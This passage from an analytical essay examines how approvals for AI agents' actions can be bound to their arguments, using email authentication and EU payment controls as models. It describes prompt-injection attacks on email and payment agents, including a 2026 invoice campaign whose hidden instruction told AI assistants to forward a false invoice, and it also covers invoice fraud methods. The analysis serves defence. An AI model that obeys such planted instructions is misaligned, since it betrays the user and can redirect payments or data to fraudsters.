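A low rate per attempt is less comforting if the attacker can keep trying. If each attempt succeeded independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts would be

1 − (1 − *p*)<sup>*n*</sup>.

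If attempts were independent, a 17.8% success rate per attempt would give an attacker about a 95% chance of succeeding at least once in 15 attempts, and near certainty in 200. The measured success rate against Opus 4.6 after 200 attempts was lower, at 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Attempts are evidently not independent, since attacks seem to fail in some situations however often they are repeated and succeed early in others. Assuming independence therefore overstates the risk here, but anyone who can email a user can usually do so more than once, so a success rate over repeated attempts is closer to the user's actual risk than the rate for a single attempt.

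The rates above are harder to use when deciding what an approval should cover, because none of them separates attacks that added an action from attacks that changed the arguments of an action the user wanted. Anthropic broke the Opus 4.6 rates down by environment, number of attempts and safeguards, and OpenAI separated direct attacks from indirect ones. Two agents could both have a rate of 2% and need quite different approvals. Approving a plan would catch nearly all the successful attacks on the first agent if they all added an action, but none of those on the second if they all changed the body of an email the user had asked for.

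General prompt-injection rates may also understate how easily attackers can manipulate the arguments of an agent's actions, as the tests with falsified data by Choi and colleagues suggested. Dai and colleagues got GPT-5.6-Luna to use their chosen arguments in most cases, although OpenAI's own tests found that indirect attacks on that model succeeded 2.94% of the time. The attacks and the scoring differ too much for a direct comparison, but a model that resists the usual attacks can still be quite easy to mislead about a file path.

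### Sorting attacks by hand

Researchers could separate extra payments from redirected ones using records of tests they have already run. AgentDojo suits this because each of its attacks pairs a user's task with an attacker's goal. Yu and colleagues, who used its chat and office tasks, labelled a run "hijacked" if the agent carried out the attacker's instruction and "resisted" if it ignored it and finished the user's task. The "hijacked" label covers both kinds of payment, but the list of tool calls shows which one occurred.

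To classify a successful attack, one would list the calls the user's task needs and compare them with the calls the agent made. If the agent made a type of call the task didn't need, the attacker added an action. If the types match but there are too many calls, the attacker added another call of a type the task needs. If the calls match one to one but a value differs, the attacker changed an argument, which can be recorded as a destination, content, an amount or a selection.

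Here is how that works for some invented banking and email cases of the kind AgentDojo simulates:

| The user asks the agent to | The attacker gets it to | What changed |
|---|---|---|
| Add up last month's spending | Send money to the attacker | Added action |
| Pay a bill saved as a file | Pay the attacker instead of the biller | Destination |
| Pay a bill saved as a file | Pay the biller, then also the attacker | Extra call of a wanted type |
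| Raise a standing order for rent | Raise it by far too much | Amount |
| Summarise unread email | Forward a private message to the attacker | Added action |
| Answer a colleague's question | Include private details in the answer | Content |
| Forward the latest contract to a client | Forward a different document | Selection |

In each of the first three rows, the attacker wants money in their account. Whether the attack counts as an added action depends on what the user asked for. A benchmark in which most users ask questions about their spending will therefore contain mostly added actions, while one in which most users pay bills will contain more extra calls and false destinations. An attack can't be classified by the attacker's goal alone, and a list of such goals would be little help in estimating how often each kind of attack occurs.

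Which approval would have helped also depends on this split. In the first and fifth rows, the user gave the agent no reason to send anything, so an approval limited to the types of action the task needs would stop both attacks, but not the other five. An approved plan with exactly one payment would also stop the third, because that attack adds a second payment. The remaining four keep to the approved number and type of calls. To catch them, the approval has to cover the values in those calls, and the person or software checking them needs the correct values for comparison.

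That last condition is easy to meet for some arguments and hard for others. A sorter can check a payment against the genuine bill. But an answer to a colleague has no single correct wording, so the sorter has to judge whether the private details belong in it, and sensible people may disagree. Researchers who want to report a separate rate for content would need to decide in advance what each message may contain, and would probably benefit from having more than one person apply the rule.

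For agents that work by clicking, the sorter must also decide at what level to compare calls. Comparing what the clicks accomplish is more useful than comparing the clicks and keystrokes themselves, because at the level of keystrokes practically everything, including the resignation letter, is a change of argument. The user's task needed an out-of-office reply and no message to the CEO, so the sorter would record one missing action and one added action. If the user had instead asked the agent to email the CEO about their holiday, the same letter would count as changed content, and an approval of one email to the CEO would have covered it.

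## What does email security show about harmful content in permitted messages?

The resignation letter in OpenAI's demonstration came from the user's own account, so there was no technical reason for the CEO's mail system to flag it. Fraudsters have exploited the same gap for years by getting into a supplier's mailbox and sending false invoices, which pass every standard sender check because they do come from the supplier's account.

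### What SPF, DKIM and DMARC check

An email has two sender addresses. Mail servers use the envelope address, for example to return a message they cannot deliver, and the reader sees the From address. Email's original design lets a sender write anything in either, so engineers later added three checks. Suppose Acme, a supplier that owns the domain acme.example, emails an invoice to a customer.

SPF (Sender Policy Framework) checks the server that delivers a message. Acme publishes a list of the servers that may send its mail. When a server delivers the invoice, the customer's mail system takes the domain from the envelope address and checks whether the server is on that domain's list. SPF does not check the From address.

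With DKIM (DomainKeys Identified Mail), Acme's server computes a short digest of the message body and some of the headers, including the From address, and signs it with a private key. The customer's system fetches the matching public key from the domain named in the signature and verifies the signature. The check fails if anyone has changed the signed text on the way. This is a kind of binding, since it ties a domain to an exact message, but the server will sign whatever a logged-in user sends.

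DMARC (Domain-based Message Authentication, Reporting and Conformance) connects these results to the address the reader sees. A message passes if SPF or DKIM has passed for a domain that matches the one in the From address. Either is enough because a legitimate message can fail SPF when another server forwards it. Acme also publishes a policy, in which it can ask receiving systems to deliver messages that fail, treat them as suspicious or reject them.

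A fraudster who wants to pose as Acme has roughly three options:

| The fraudster writes from | SPF | DKIM | DMARC |
|---|---|---|---|
| Their own domain, with Acme's address in the From line | Passes for the fraudster's domain | Passes for the fraudster's domain | Fails, because neither result is for Acme |
| A lookalike domain they registered | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| Acme's real account | Passes | Passes | Passes |

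DMARC was an improvement, because without it the fraudster in the first row could pass the other two checks while showing Acme's address. The case in the second row is common enough to appear in vendors' case reports. *The $47,320 Invoice That Came With a W-9*, by the email security vendor IRONSCALES, mentions a message that passed all three checks and was sent to an accounts-payable mailbox from a newly registered imitation of LinkedIn's domain.

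All three results in the third row are correct, because Acme's server sent the message, Acme's key signed it and the From address is Acme's. None of the checks covers who was logged in or whether the bank account on the invoice belongs to Acme.

A misled agent belongs in that row too, although nobody has stolen a password. If an attacker gets the assistant to add a false request to the schedule email, the email still comes from the user's account, so it passes whichever of these checks John's mail system applies.

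### Business email compromise

The FBI's *2025 IC3 Annual Report* (2026) defines business email compromise as a scam aimed at businesses or individuals who work with suppliers or regularly pay by wire transfer. Fraudsters compromise email accounts or other channels, such as phone numbers and virtual meetings, to obtain unauthorised transfers. The Australian cyber security agency's description, as summarised in Dynamic Business' *The new phishing trick aimed at the AI reading your inbox*, is a little more explicit that criminals either compromise a genuine account or impersonate one, often a supplier's or an executive's.

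The FBI's figures come from complaints to its Internet Crime Complaint Center, known as IC3:

| Year | Complaints | Reported losses |
|---|---|---|
| 2023 | 21,489 | $2.95 billion |
| 2024 | 21,442 | $2.77 billion |
| 2025 | 24,768 | $3.05 billion |

Only investment fraud cost victims more than business email compromise in 2025. Business email compromise made up about 2.5% of all complaints but about 15% of losses, with an average loss of roughly $123,000 per complaint, compared with about $1,100 for ordinary phishing. CyberScoop points out that an unknown number of victims never report, so the true total could be a good deal higher.

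The FBI's totals do not separate compromised accounts from impersonated ones, so we cannot tell from them how much of the money followed an email that passed all three checks. Two of the report's cases illustrate the difference. In March 2025, an elderly person in Missouri who was closing a property deal got payment instructions in what the FBI calls a compromised email from the title company, the firm handling the sale. The instructions directed more than $1.3 million to a fraudulent account. In August, home buyers sent over $449,000 after receiving an email that impersonated their lawyers.

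Both are cases of argument hijacking, with a person in place of the agent. The victims wanted to make the payment, and the fraudster changed where it went.

A fraudster with access to a mailbox can also wait for a real conversation about a payment and reply at the right moment, which security companies call thread hijacking. The recipient has good reason to trust the reply because the account and the earlier messages are genuine. According to Baskin, in *Key findings from the 2026 Sublime Email Threat Research Report*, thread hijacking overtook older methods of business email compromise in 2025, though this finding is based on the mail that one vendor handles.

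Inventing the conversation is easier, because the earlier messages at the bottom of an email are ordinary body text that anyone can type. DKIM does not help, because a valid signature only confirms that the latest sender's domain sent that text, not that the people quoted in it wrote any of it.

IRONSCALES describes an email demanding $74,250 that reached the accounts-payable address of a healthcare services company. It came from a small business's hijacked mailbox, so it passed the SPF sender check. The email included three invented replies below the demand, and in one of them someone from the recipient's finance department appeared to authorise the payment. Automated screening classified the email with high confidence as promotional bulk mail, but a human analyst recognised it as fraud.

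Douglas (2026), in *Signal & Noise, Volume 1*, tells a similar story about a $64,294.12 invoice from a nonexistent supplier, with a forged approval from an executive. The accounts-payable staff thought the invoice was slightly off and asked security analysts to investigate, and the company paid nothing.

Fraudsters also do this in bulk. In a campaign that Microsoft (2026) described in September, they sent over a million emails in the names of target companies' CEOs, asking for nearly $50,000. Each email included a forged invoice and a forged exchange between the CEO and ServiceNow, a software company. The payment-security firm Trustmi counted about 255 attempts in the first half of 2026 that presented a payment as already decided by an executive. SecurityInfoWatch reports that these were more than four in ten of the attempts Trustmi analysed.

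In these cases the attacker forged the approval. An agent that searches the inbox to check whether a manager approved a payment could easily mistake one of these threads for a real approval. Permission has to reach the agent through a channel that outsiders can't write to, which rules out quoted emails.

Software can catch some invented email threads by checking them against a company's mail records. Sublime Security's *Attack spotlight* describes a message that asked a company to change the destination of a large invoice payment. The message included supposed earlier correspondence, but the sender's domain had never contacted the company before. Software could find this mismatch using only the company's own mail records. The same check would not catch a fraudster who had joined a real thread, because the earlier correspondence would be genuine.

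### Email sent to the wrong person

People in an organisation can also send harmful email by mistake, with no attacker involved. For example, someone types "John", accepts the address the software suggests and sends a contract to the wrong John. The UK's Information Commissioner's Office, to which organisations must report many breaches of personal data, has for years listed personal data emailed to the wrong recipient among the most common incidents. These counts are only a rough guide to how often it happens, because they include only mistakes that someone noticed and reported, and they omit the number of emails sent correctly.

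Organisations use several controls on outgoing mail. The simplest warns the sender when a recipient's email domain differs from the organisation's own. This would catch a message addressed to the wrong John if he worked at another organisation, but not if he worked at the sender's.

The warning also appears on a lot of correct email. Suppose an office sends 3,000 messages to outside recipients, and one is addressed to the wrong person. The software would interrupt people 3,000 times to give one of them a chance to notice a mistake, and people tend to stop reading warnings they see that often. A narrower warning, for recipients the sender has never written to or who don't usually appear together, would interrupt people less often but miss more mistakes, since the wrong recipient may be an old contact.

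A data-loss filter searches outgoing messages and their attachments for things the organisation doesn't want to send out, such as payment card numbers, identity numbers or documents marked confidential. If it finds any, it blocks the message, holds it or asks the sender to confirm. Payment card numbers are easy to recognise because the last digit is calculated from the others, so a filter that checks it can rule out nine in ten random numbers of the same length. A doctor's appointment in a schedule has no such structure, and a filter that looks only for patterns can't take into account who will read the schedule.

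Delayed sending gives the sender time to cancel a message but doesn't examine the message itself. Gmail, for instance, can hold a message for up to 30 seconds. This helps because people often notice a mistake just after pressing send. It helps much less when an agent sends the email and the user isn't watching, since nobody will notice the mistake in time.

Saving an email as a draft delays it until someone chooses to send it. Nylas, which sells email software to developers, recommends in its documentation that agents write drafts and leave the sending to a person. If an attacker has influenced a reply, the user can then delete it with one click, whereas a sent email can't be recalled. Nylas says that 80% of useful work by email agents, such as sorting, summarising and drafting, doesn't require the ability to send. I wouldn't put much weight on that number because it's a vendor's estimate,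 but the advice seems right for any agent whose user reads the drafts.

### The invoice campaign of October 2026

On 22 October 2026, Sublime Security observed a campaign that combined ordinary invoice fraud with an attack on AI assistants. The company's page *Shut down prompt injection attacks targeting AI email agents and tools* lists its 26 October report on the campaign. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) gives a fuller account.

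The emails went mostly to financial controllers, who oversee a company's accounts. Each appeared to come from a founder or chief executive of the controller's company and contained an invoice for about $88,000, supposedly from a North American cybersecurity firm. The emails also included an invented reply chain, and a 10% discount that was about to expire gave the controller a reason to hurry.

The emails also contained an instruction that a human reader could not see but an AI assistant might. The instruction was to forward the email and its invoice, unchanged, to what looked like an accounts-payable address at the target's company.

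```
asked for:       summarize(new email)
attacker wants:  forward(THE FALSE INVOICE, ACCOUNTS PAYABLE)
```

If the user only wanted a summary, forwarding the invoice would be an added action. But some companies want an agent to forward invoices to accounts payable. There, forwarding is expected, and the attacker has only chosen which invoice the agent sends. A person asked to approve the call would see a familiar colleague's address and an ordinary-looking invoice.

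If an agent did forward the email, accounts payable would receive the invoice from the controller's real account, whereas the attacker had to impersonate an executive in the original. The staff might reasonably assume that the controller, whose job is to deal with invoices, had looked at it.

Trent names no agent known to have forwarded the invoice and no company known to have paid it. When Sublime tried the email on several models, some never mentioned the hidden instruction, some included it in a summary, and some identified the attack and advised the user to report it. Trent reports no case of a model forwarding the email, but does not say which models Sublime used or whether they had a tool for forwarding. The campaign is good evidence that criminals are trying to use email agents in their attacks, but it provides no evidence that they have succeeded.

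Such attempts seem fairly new. Darktrace's *Comment les attaques par injection de prompt transmises par email peuvent cibler* (2026) reported in May that prompt injection had only a handful of confirmed victims. In June, Scholten and Filar (2026) wrote in *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection* that almost all the prompt injections Sublime had seen in real email were meant to make security software classify a malicious message as harmless. Two weeks earlier, however, Mascellino (2026) reported in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* that the security firm Barracuda had found phishing emails aimed at both people and their AI assistants. By July, criminals were advertising tools for prompt injection, some from about $150 a month, according to Proofpoint research described in eSecurity Planet's *Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*.

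The hidden instruction may be the easiest part of the October emails to detect. Software can compare the text a person would see with the text a model would receive, and a genuine invoice has little reason to contain instructions that only the model receives. Trent recommends removing invisible characters before a model reads the message, which would deal with this instruction but leave the false invoice and the invented reply chain. In September, Ahmed (2026) reported in *Fake Email Thread Tricks AI Summarizer Without Hidden Text* that an invented thread containing no hidden text had misled an AI summariser.

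### Which of these controls work for agents?

Controls on incoming mail carry over fairly directly to AI agents. *Anyone can email your agent (MachineMail)* (Neely, 2026) describes a service that gives agents their own inboxes and scores each incoming message for hostile intent before the agent reads it. The service works much like a person's spam filter and will presumably miss some well-written messages for the same reasons.

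On the outgoing side, the controls help with some attacks and do nothing about others. This is how two of them would probably handle attacks on an agent that writes email for an employee, assuming that John and the CEO work at the same company as the user:

| What the attacker gets the agent to do | Warning about external recipients | Data-loss filter |
|---|---|---|
| Forward tax documents to a stranger | Appears | Probably catches it |
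| Include a doctor's appointment in the schedule for John | Does not appear | Probably misses it |
| Add a false request to the schedule for John | Does not appear | Misses it |
| Send the CEO a resignation letter | Does not appear | Misses it |
| Forward the October invoice to accounts payable | Does not appear | Misses it |

The check in the first row, on where data is going, is worth having. OpenAI says that most of the attacks it sees try to extract secrets, and this check does not depend on the model noticing the attack. Developers can run it on every tool call and make it stricter for an agent than for an employee, for example by allowing email only to people the user named in the request. The check also has to cover web addresses inside a message, as the Slack leak showed.

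In the last three rows, nothing secret goes to an outsider. The harm comes from what a colleague will believe or do after reading the message, and neither control checks for that.

Email security companies can detect some compromised accounts by looking for unusual behaviour, such as a login from a new country or a first request for money from someone who never handles invoices. This can reveal an intruder even when the message is convincing. It is likely to work less well on a misled agent, which uses its normal login and server and may write in its usual style. An unusual recipient or request could still stand out, but a request that fits the user's job probably would not.

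Better filters also cannot distinguish some fraudulent emails from genuine ones if they see only the emails. Suppose Acme changes banks and emails a customer its new account number. A month later, an intruder in the same mailbox sends the same email with a different account number. Both emails pass SPF, DKIM and DMARC. They differ only in the account number, and both numbers are well formed, so the filter has no basis for stopping just the false one.

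To tell them apart, someone needs information from outside the email. Before paying, the customer could call Acme on a number they already had or compare the account with independent records. The same applies to a false appointment in the schedule email. If an invitation lists a ten o'clock meeting with a client, a filter can establish who sent it, but only the user or the client can say whether they agreed to meet.

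## How do payment controls tie approval to payee and amount?

Banks have long faced a similar problem. A customer approves a payment on a screen, but an intruder may have tampered with the software that then carries the order. The bank has to establish that the order it receives is the one the customer approved. Since 2019, banks in the EU have had to do this through dynamic linking, a form of binding.

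Article 5 of the EU's Delegated Regulation 2018/389 ties a payer's approval to the amount and payee when a bank uses strong customer authentication for an online payment. Strong customer authentication means that customers prove who they are in at least two independent ways, for example with a fingerprint and a phone that the bank has registered. The bank must make the payer aware of the amount and the payee. The payer's consent then produces an authentication code specific to both, and the bank must not accept the code if either changes.

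In tool-call terms, this ties approval to two arguments, the amount and the destination, but not to the rest of the order, such as the message to the payee.

### A supplier invoice for €4,800

Suppose a customer owes €4,800 to Acme, the supplier from the email examples, and enters the payment on a laptop. OneSpan's *Performing dynamic linking in a compliant, convenient way*, a page from an authentication software vendor, describes one common way to approve it. The customer gets a notification on their phone and opens the bank's app, which shows the payment details. They confirm with a fingerprint or face scan. The phone then calculates a code from those details and sends it to the bank.

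The regulation leaves the technology open. Its introduction, in the Official Journal of the European Union (2018), mentions one-time passwords and digital signatures among the possibilities. A simple version would be

*c* = *f*(*k*, 4800.00, *A*, *r*),

where *A* is Acme's account number, *k* is a secret key that only the phone and the bank hold, and *r* is a fresh number for this payment, so that nobody can reuse an old code. The function *f* scrambles its inputs so thoroughly that nobody without the key can work out the code for a different payment.

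Now suppose malware on the laptop replaces Acme's account with the fraudster's, *F*, after the customer has approved. The bank calculates the code again from the order it actually received (the codes here are invented):

```
customer approved:   4,800.00 to A         -> code 482 913
bank receives:       4,800.00 to F, with code 482 913
bank calculates:     4,800.00 to F         -> code 706 158
```

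The codes differ, so the bank rejects the order. It would also reject the order if the malware had changed only the amount, to €48,000. A six-digit code for an altered order has about a one in a million chance of matching the old code.

This works because the malware changed the account after the details had reached the phone. If it changes the account before then, the phone calculates a valid code for the fraudster's account. The customer can still refuse the payment, because the phone also displays that account. But malware on the phone could display Acme's account while the code covers the fraudster's. For this reason, Article 5 also requires banks to protect the information shown to the payer from tampering at every stage of the authentication.

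| Where the account number changes | Account the customer sees | Result |
|---|---|---|
| In the order, after approval | Acme's | The code fails and the bank rejects the order |
| On the laptop, before approval | The fraudster's | The code is valid unless the customer refuses |
| On the phone's display | Acme's | The code is valid for the fraudster's account |
| On the invoice | The fraudster's, as on the invoice | The code is valid |

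The rule is looser for batches of payments, where the code has to be specific only to the total amount and the payees. According to a question submitted to the European Banking Authority (EBA), one batch file might contain thousands of account numbers. If a batch paid €4,800 to Acme and €200 to a small supplier controlled by a fraudster, malware could swap the two amounts without changing the total or the payees. A code that met only the bare wording of the rule would still be valid, and the fraudster would gain €4,600. A bank can prevent this by calculating the code over every line of the file. Anyone who approves a list of payments drawn up by an agent should want the same protection, because the total can be correct even when individual payments are wrong.

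### How much fraud involves an altered order?

The European Banking Authority and European Central Bank's *2025 Report on Payment Fraud* covers the European Economic Area up to the end of 2024. Fraudulent credit transfers, the ordinary bank transfers people use to pay invoices, came to €2.5 billion that year, 24% more than in 2023. Fraudsters altered the payer's order in only 1% to 2% of this fraud by value. In 74%, they manipulated the payer into making the payment, up from 65% the year before. In nearly all the rest, they issued the order themselves, for example with stolen login details.

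Dynamic linking may partly explain the first of those figures. When it published the report, the EBA (2025) said that strong authentication remains effective against the kinds of fraud it was designed for, especially with cards. But the data start in 2022, when the rule already applied, so they can't be used to compare fraud before and after it. Fraudsters may also have little interest in malware if they can persuade people to pay. Whatever the explanation, most of the money fraudsters now take through bank transfers goes where the payer told the bank to send it.

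The report also shows that transfers with strong authentication had higher fraud rates than transfers without it. The EBA and ECB attribute this to the kinds of payment involved, since banks tend to skip authentication for safe payments, such as transfers between a customer's own accounts.

One of the exemptions resembles the "always allow" button on agents. A customer can authenticate once to put a payee on a list of trusted beneficiaries, and the bank can skip authentication for later payments to that payee. The EBA and ECB reported that these payments had a higher fraud rate than credit transfers in general, but didn't explain why. One possible reason is that some customers add a fraudster's account to the list, in which case a single mistaken approval covers every later payment to that account.

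More recent national figures are patchy. In Cyprus, manipulation of the payer accounted for 59% of fraudulent credit transfers in the first half of 2025, according to Cyprus Mail's *Card fraud drives surge in Cyprus payment scams* (2026). The Irish Times' *Central Bank records sharp jump in fraudulent payments to €180m* (2026) reports that losses across all payment types in Ireland rose by more than a quarter in 2025.

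### When the invoice names the fraudster's account

In the last row of the table, the fraudster has got into Acme's mailbox, or imitated it, and sent an invoice with a different account number. Nobody has tampered with the bank's software or the customer's devices. The customer copies the account number from the invoice, so the number on the phone matches it. The customer approves the payment, and the bank checks the code and sends €4,800 to the fraudster.

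This is authorised push payment fraud. In a push payment, the payer instructs the bank to send the money, whereas with a card or a direct debit the payee collects it. *Authorised Payment Fraud* (Jones, Kraft and Subramaniam, 2026) defines authorised fraud as fraud in which criminals mislead or coerce people into initiating or approving payments. In unauthorised fraud, criminals use stolen credentials or compromised systems to pay without the victim's knowledge.

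The customer meant to pay Acme but approved a payment to an account number. Article 5 requires the code to match "the payee agreed to by the payer", and the customer did agree to that account. The code cannot ensure that the account belongs to Acme, because neither the phone nor the bank has data showing whom the customer owes.

Using an agent changes little about this. If the agent copies the false number, as in Girrens and Wang's invoice attack, a person who approves the payment in the bank's app will see the same number. They are more likely than the agent to notice the fraud only if they know Acme's real number or look it up.

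### Checks that use other information

The remaining controls rely on something outside the invoice. There is little evidence on how well they work. Jones and colleagues profile 15 widely used measures against authorised fraud but decline to judge how effective each one is, partly because that depends heavily on conditions that vary by country.

Name checks are the most widespread of these controls. The UK's version, Confirmation of Payee, began in 2020 at the largest banks. The payer enters a name along with the account number. Before sending the money, the payer's bank asks the receiving bank whether that name belongs to the account. The result can be a match, a close match, no match or "unavailable". Banks in the euro area have had to offer a similar service, Verification of Payee, since October 2025.

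Here is how such a check would probably respond to different versions of the false invoice:

| The fraudster's account is in the name of | The customer types | Likely answer |
|---|---|---|
| A private individual | Acme | No match |
| A company with a very similar name | Acme | Match or close match |
| A "collection agency" named on the invoice | The agency's name | Match |
| Anyone, at a bank outside the scheme | Acme | Unavailable |

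The check is good at catching the first version, which makes it safer than sending money to an account number alone. In the third, the fraudster supplied both the name and the number, so the check confirms only that they match. The same thing could easily happen with an ordinary false invoice if an agent copies both the payee's name and the account number from it. The name should come from the user's request or the company's own list of suppliers.

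The EU rules also let customers that are not consumers opt out of the check when they submit many payments as a package. Many companies pay their suppliers this way.

The EBA and ECB's figures can't show the effect of the euro-area requirement because they end before it began. The Bank of Portugal's service checked 404 million payments in its first year, according to The Portugal Brief's *Victims of Fake Bank Calls Would Get Their Money Back* (2026), but that count measures only how often people used it. The UK has a longer record. UK Finance, the banks' trade body, put losses to authorised push payment fraud at about £421 million in 2020, £583 million in 2021 and £451 million in 2024. These figures are hard to interpret because online payments, warnings from banks and new kinds of scam spread over the same period as name checks. They do rule out the idea that name checks would nearly eliminate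 this kind of fraud.

Payee checks also work less well across borders. PYMNTS's *Europe’s Payee Checks Set the Pace as US Plans Take Shape* (2026) notes that they still depend on systems built country by country. Cross-border transfers made up about a fifth of the value of credit transfers in the EBA and ECB's data, but 40% to 50% of the value of the fraud. Some of those payments were between euro-area countries, where the check now applies.

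#### Calling the supplier

In a call-back, someone at the customer's company rings Acme to ask whether it has changed its account, which the name check cannot show. The caller has to use a number from an old contract or an existing supplier record, because a fraudster who writes a false account number can also write a false phone number beside it. For the same reason, an incoming call that "confirms" the change is very weak evidence.

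The call is needed only when an account is new or has changed. Suppose a company has 200 suppliers, of whom 40 change their details in a year. If each call takes 15 minutes, the calls take ten hours a year. The average reported loss from business email compromise is about $123,000, based on the FBI's figures, so the calls would be worthwhile even if they prevented only one such loss in a century. This calculation leaves out the delay to genuine payments, but it suggests that a company doesn't need strong evidence that the calls work to justify making them.

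Direct evidence that call-backs prevent fraud is scarce, because companies seldom publish how many false changes their calls uncover. The case for call-backs rests mainly on how they work. A fraudster who controls Acme's mailbox would also have to control Acme's phone line, deceive whoever answers, or have altered the customer's records earlier.

#### A second approver

Many companies require two people to approve a large payment. This makes it harder for a dishonest employee to steal and catches some careless mistakes. How much it helps against a false invoice depends on what the second person looks at.

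Let *r* be the share of false invoices that nobody could recognise from the documents alone, and let *q* be the chance that one person misses any of the others. If two people make their mistakes independently, the share of false invoices that gets past both is

*r* + (1 − *r*)*q*².

As an invented example, suppose *r* is 0.8 and *q* is 0.5. One approver would let through 90% of false invoices, and two would let through 85%. A convincing invoice sent from a supplier's real account plausibly belongs in the first group. The second approver would do far more good by ringing Acme than by rereading the invoice.

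The EBA and ECB's report offers some indirect evidence about second approvers. Banks can skip strong authentication for business customers who pay through secure corporate systems, which often require two approvers. The fraud rate on those payments was around 0.0001% by value, roughly a tenth of the rate for all credit transfers. But these systems differ from ordinary online banking in several other ways, and according to the report, fraudsters are less likely to target such payments, so the second approver shouldn't be credited with the whole difference.

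#### Holding the payment

A hold gives people time to discover fraud before the money is gone. Since October 2024, UK law has allowed a bank to delay a payment by up to four business days if it has reasonable grounds to suspect fraud. The EU's new payment regulation, which is not yet in force, delays increases to spending limits. If a customer sets a limit and later raises it through an app or by phone, the higher limit takes effect only after a delay, by default four hours. The Portugal Brief explains that customers can shorten or switch off the delay, but that this change is itself subject to the delay. A fraudster who persuades someone to raise a limit therefore cannot empty the account immediately.

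The case for stopping fraud before the money leaves is fairly strong. In 2024, fraudulent credit transfers came to €2.5 billion and losses to €2.2 billion, which suggests that banks recovered only about an eighth of the money. The estimate is rough because banks may record a loss in a later period than the fraud.

Evidence that faster payments mean more fraud is mixed. From 2022 to 2024, the number of instant transfers in the EU countries with full data rose by 98% and the number of fraudulent ones by 175%. But the total value of fraudulent instant transfers grew more slowly than that of all instant transfers, and the average fraudulent instant transfer was less than half the size of the average fraudulent ordinary one. These figures don't measure the effect of holding payments. A hold helps only if someone uses the time to check, because a customer who believes a false invoice will probably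 still believe it a few days later.

### Signers who could not read what they approved

In February 2025, hackers whom the FBI linked to North Korea stole about $1.5 billion from Bybit, a cryptocurrency exchange. Bybit kept the money in a wallet that could pay out only when several people had signed. The hackers altered the website where those people reviewed transactions, so they all approved the same false display.

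```
signers saw:     transfer(funds, Bybit's own wallet)
signers signed:  change_control(wallet, THE ATTACKERS' CODE)
```

The website showed a routine transfer between two of Bybit's wallets, but the data sent to the signers' hardware devices gave the attackers control of the wallet. The devices displayed that data in a form that a person could not readily interpret. The signers approved it, and the attackers emptied the wallet.

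The binding worked, because each signature was valid only for the data that the signer's device had received, and any later change would have invalidated it. The failure was in the other half of Article 5, that payers should know what they are approving and see it on a display nobody has tampered with. More signers would have added little protection while they all relied on the same website. A separate device that translated the data into "give control of this wallet to someone else" would probably have stopped the theft.

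Agents that show users a raw command raise a similar problem. A developer may be able to read the command, but most other people cannot, and for them an accurate display is little better than a false one. Even when a display is clear, people may not read it closely, and experiments have examined whether they do.

### Who bears the loss?

In the EU, this depends largely on whether the law treats a payment as authorised. In October 2026, the EU's highest court decided a case about an unauthorised payment (Court of Justice of the European Union, *Payment services*, 2026). A woman in Poland was selling something online when a supposed buyer sent her a link to an imitation of her bank's website. She entered her login details, and the fraudster used them to transfer about €700. The bank refused to refund her, claiming she had been grossly negligent. The court ruled that the bank had to refund her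 immediately, but could try to recover the money from her afterwards if it could prove gross negligence. A bank may withhold the immediate refund only if it has reasonable grounds to suspect that the customer committed fraud and reports those grounds to the authorities.

If the fraudster had instead persuaded her to make the transfer herself, the payment would probably have counted as authorised, and she would have had no such right. Customers bore around 85% of the losses on credit transfers in 2024, compared with 38% for cards. The EBA and ECB suggest that one reason may be a tendency to treat every payment with strong authentication as authorised. They also note that, as legal thinking has developed, an authenticated payment cannot automatically be assumed to be authorised. The distinction matters for any kind of approval. A valid code is good evidence that the customer confirmed the payment,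 but it doesn't establish what they thought they were agreeing to.

UK banks bear much of the loss when a fraudster tricks a consumer into sending money. *Agentic AI in the payments chain* (2026), an article by the law firm Freshfields, summarises the Payment Systems Regulator's rules. The sending bank must reimburse the consumer in most cases, up to £85,000, and the receiving bank covers half of that. A consumer tricked into sending £200,000, for example, would get back £85,000 and lose the other £115,000. Paying half gives the receiving bank a reason to check more carefully who opens accounts with it, which the sending bank can't control.

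The UK scheme started in October 2024. In the regulator's early figures, firms returned well over four-fifths of the money lost in claims covered by the rules. That shows the scheme compensates victims, but not that it prevents fraud. UK Finance reported that losses to authorised push payment fraud rose 12% in the first half of 2025, to £257.5 million, although the number of cases fell.

The EU has chosen a much narrower rule. *Two EU sites, two clocks* (Berryman, 2026) reports that the Council, which represents the member states' governments, adopted its position on the new regulation on 29 October 2026 by 27 votes to none. A committee of the European Parliament approved the text on 1 December, and the Parliament's calendar lists a final vote for 14 December. Most of the regulation applies 21 months after it enters into force, so autumn 2028 at the earliest.

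Under the new rule, a bank must refund a consumer who was manipulated by a fraudster posing as the consumer's own bank. The consumer must notify the bank without undue delay and report the fraud to the police. The bank then has 15 business days to pay or to explain its refusal in writing, and it can refuse only with objective reasons to suspect fraud or gross negligence. The Portugal Brief points out that the rule doesn't cover fraudsters who pose as anyone else, such as a relative or a police officer.

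That leaves out the Acme invoice, where the fraudster posed as a supplier. This is roughly where the loss would fall:

| Who pays the false invoice | UK, now | EU, under the new impersonation rule |
|---|---|---|
| A consumer | The banks reimburse up to £85,000 in most cases | No refund |
| A business with fewer than ten employees | Usually the same as for a consumer | No refund |
| A larger company | No reimbursement under the scheme | No refund |

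The new EU regulation creates one exception. It extends the name check to all credit transfers, 27 months after it enters into force, and a bank that carries out the check wrongly must refund the payment. A company might recover the €4,800 if its bank reported a match for an account that was not in Acme's name. If the bank correctly warned of a mismatch and the company paid anyway, the company would have no claim under that provision.

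### When an agent makes the payment

An agent can prepare a payment and leave the customer to approve it in the bank's app. Dynamic linking is especially useful then, because the app shows the amount and the payee on a display the agent doesn't control. If the agent takes a false account number from its notes but tells the customer "I'm paying Acme", the app will still show the account receiving the money, and a name check may reveal that it isn't Acme's.

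However, people often want an agent to pay without them. Freshfields points out that strong authentication normally relies on a person to enter a PIN, provide a fingerprint or respond to a notification. An agent can't do these things in the usual sense, and current UK and EU rules don't explicitly provide for payments started by something other than a person. In one solution the firm describes, the customer authenticates once and gives the agent a token, limited in time and scope, as proof. In another, the agent can spend up to a fixed budget from a prepaid wallet without asking about each payment.

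Google's Agent Payments Protocol, first released in September 2025, records what the customer agreed to in mandates, which are statements the customer signs with a cryptographic key so that anyone involved can check them later. If the customer is present for the purchase, they sign a cart mandate that states exactly what is being bought. If the agent will buy later on its own, they sign an intent mandate that sets conditions for the purchase. The payment network also receives a third document, which records that an agent took part and whether the customer was present.

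```
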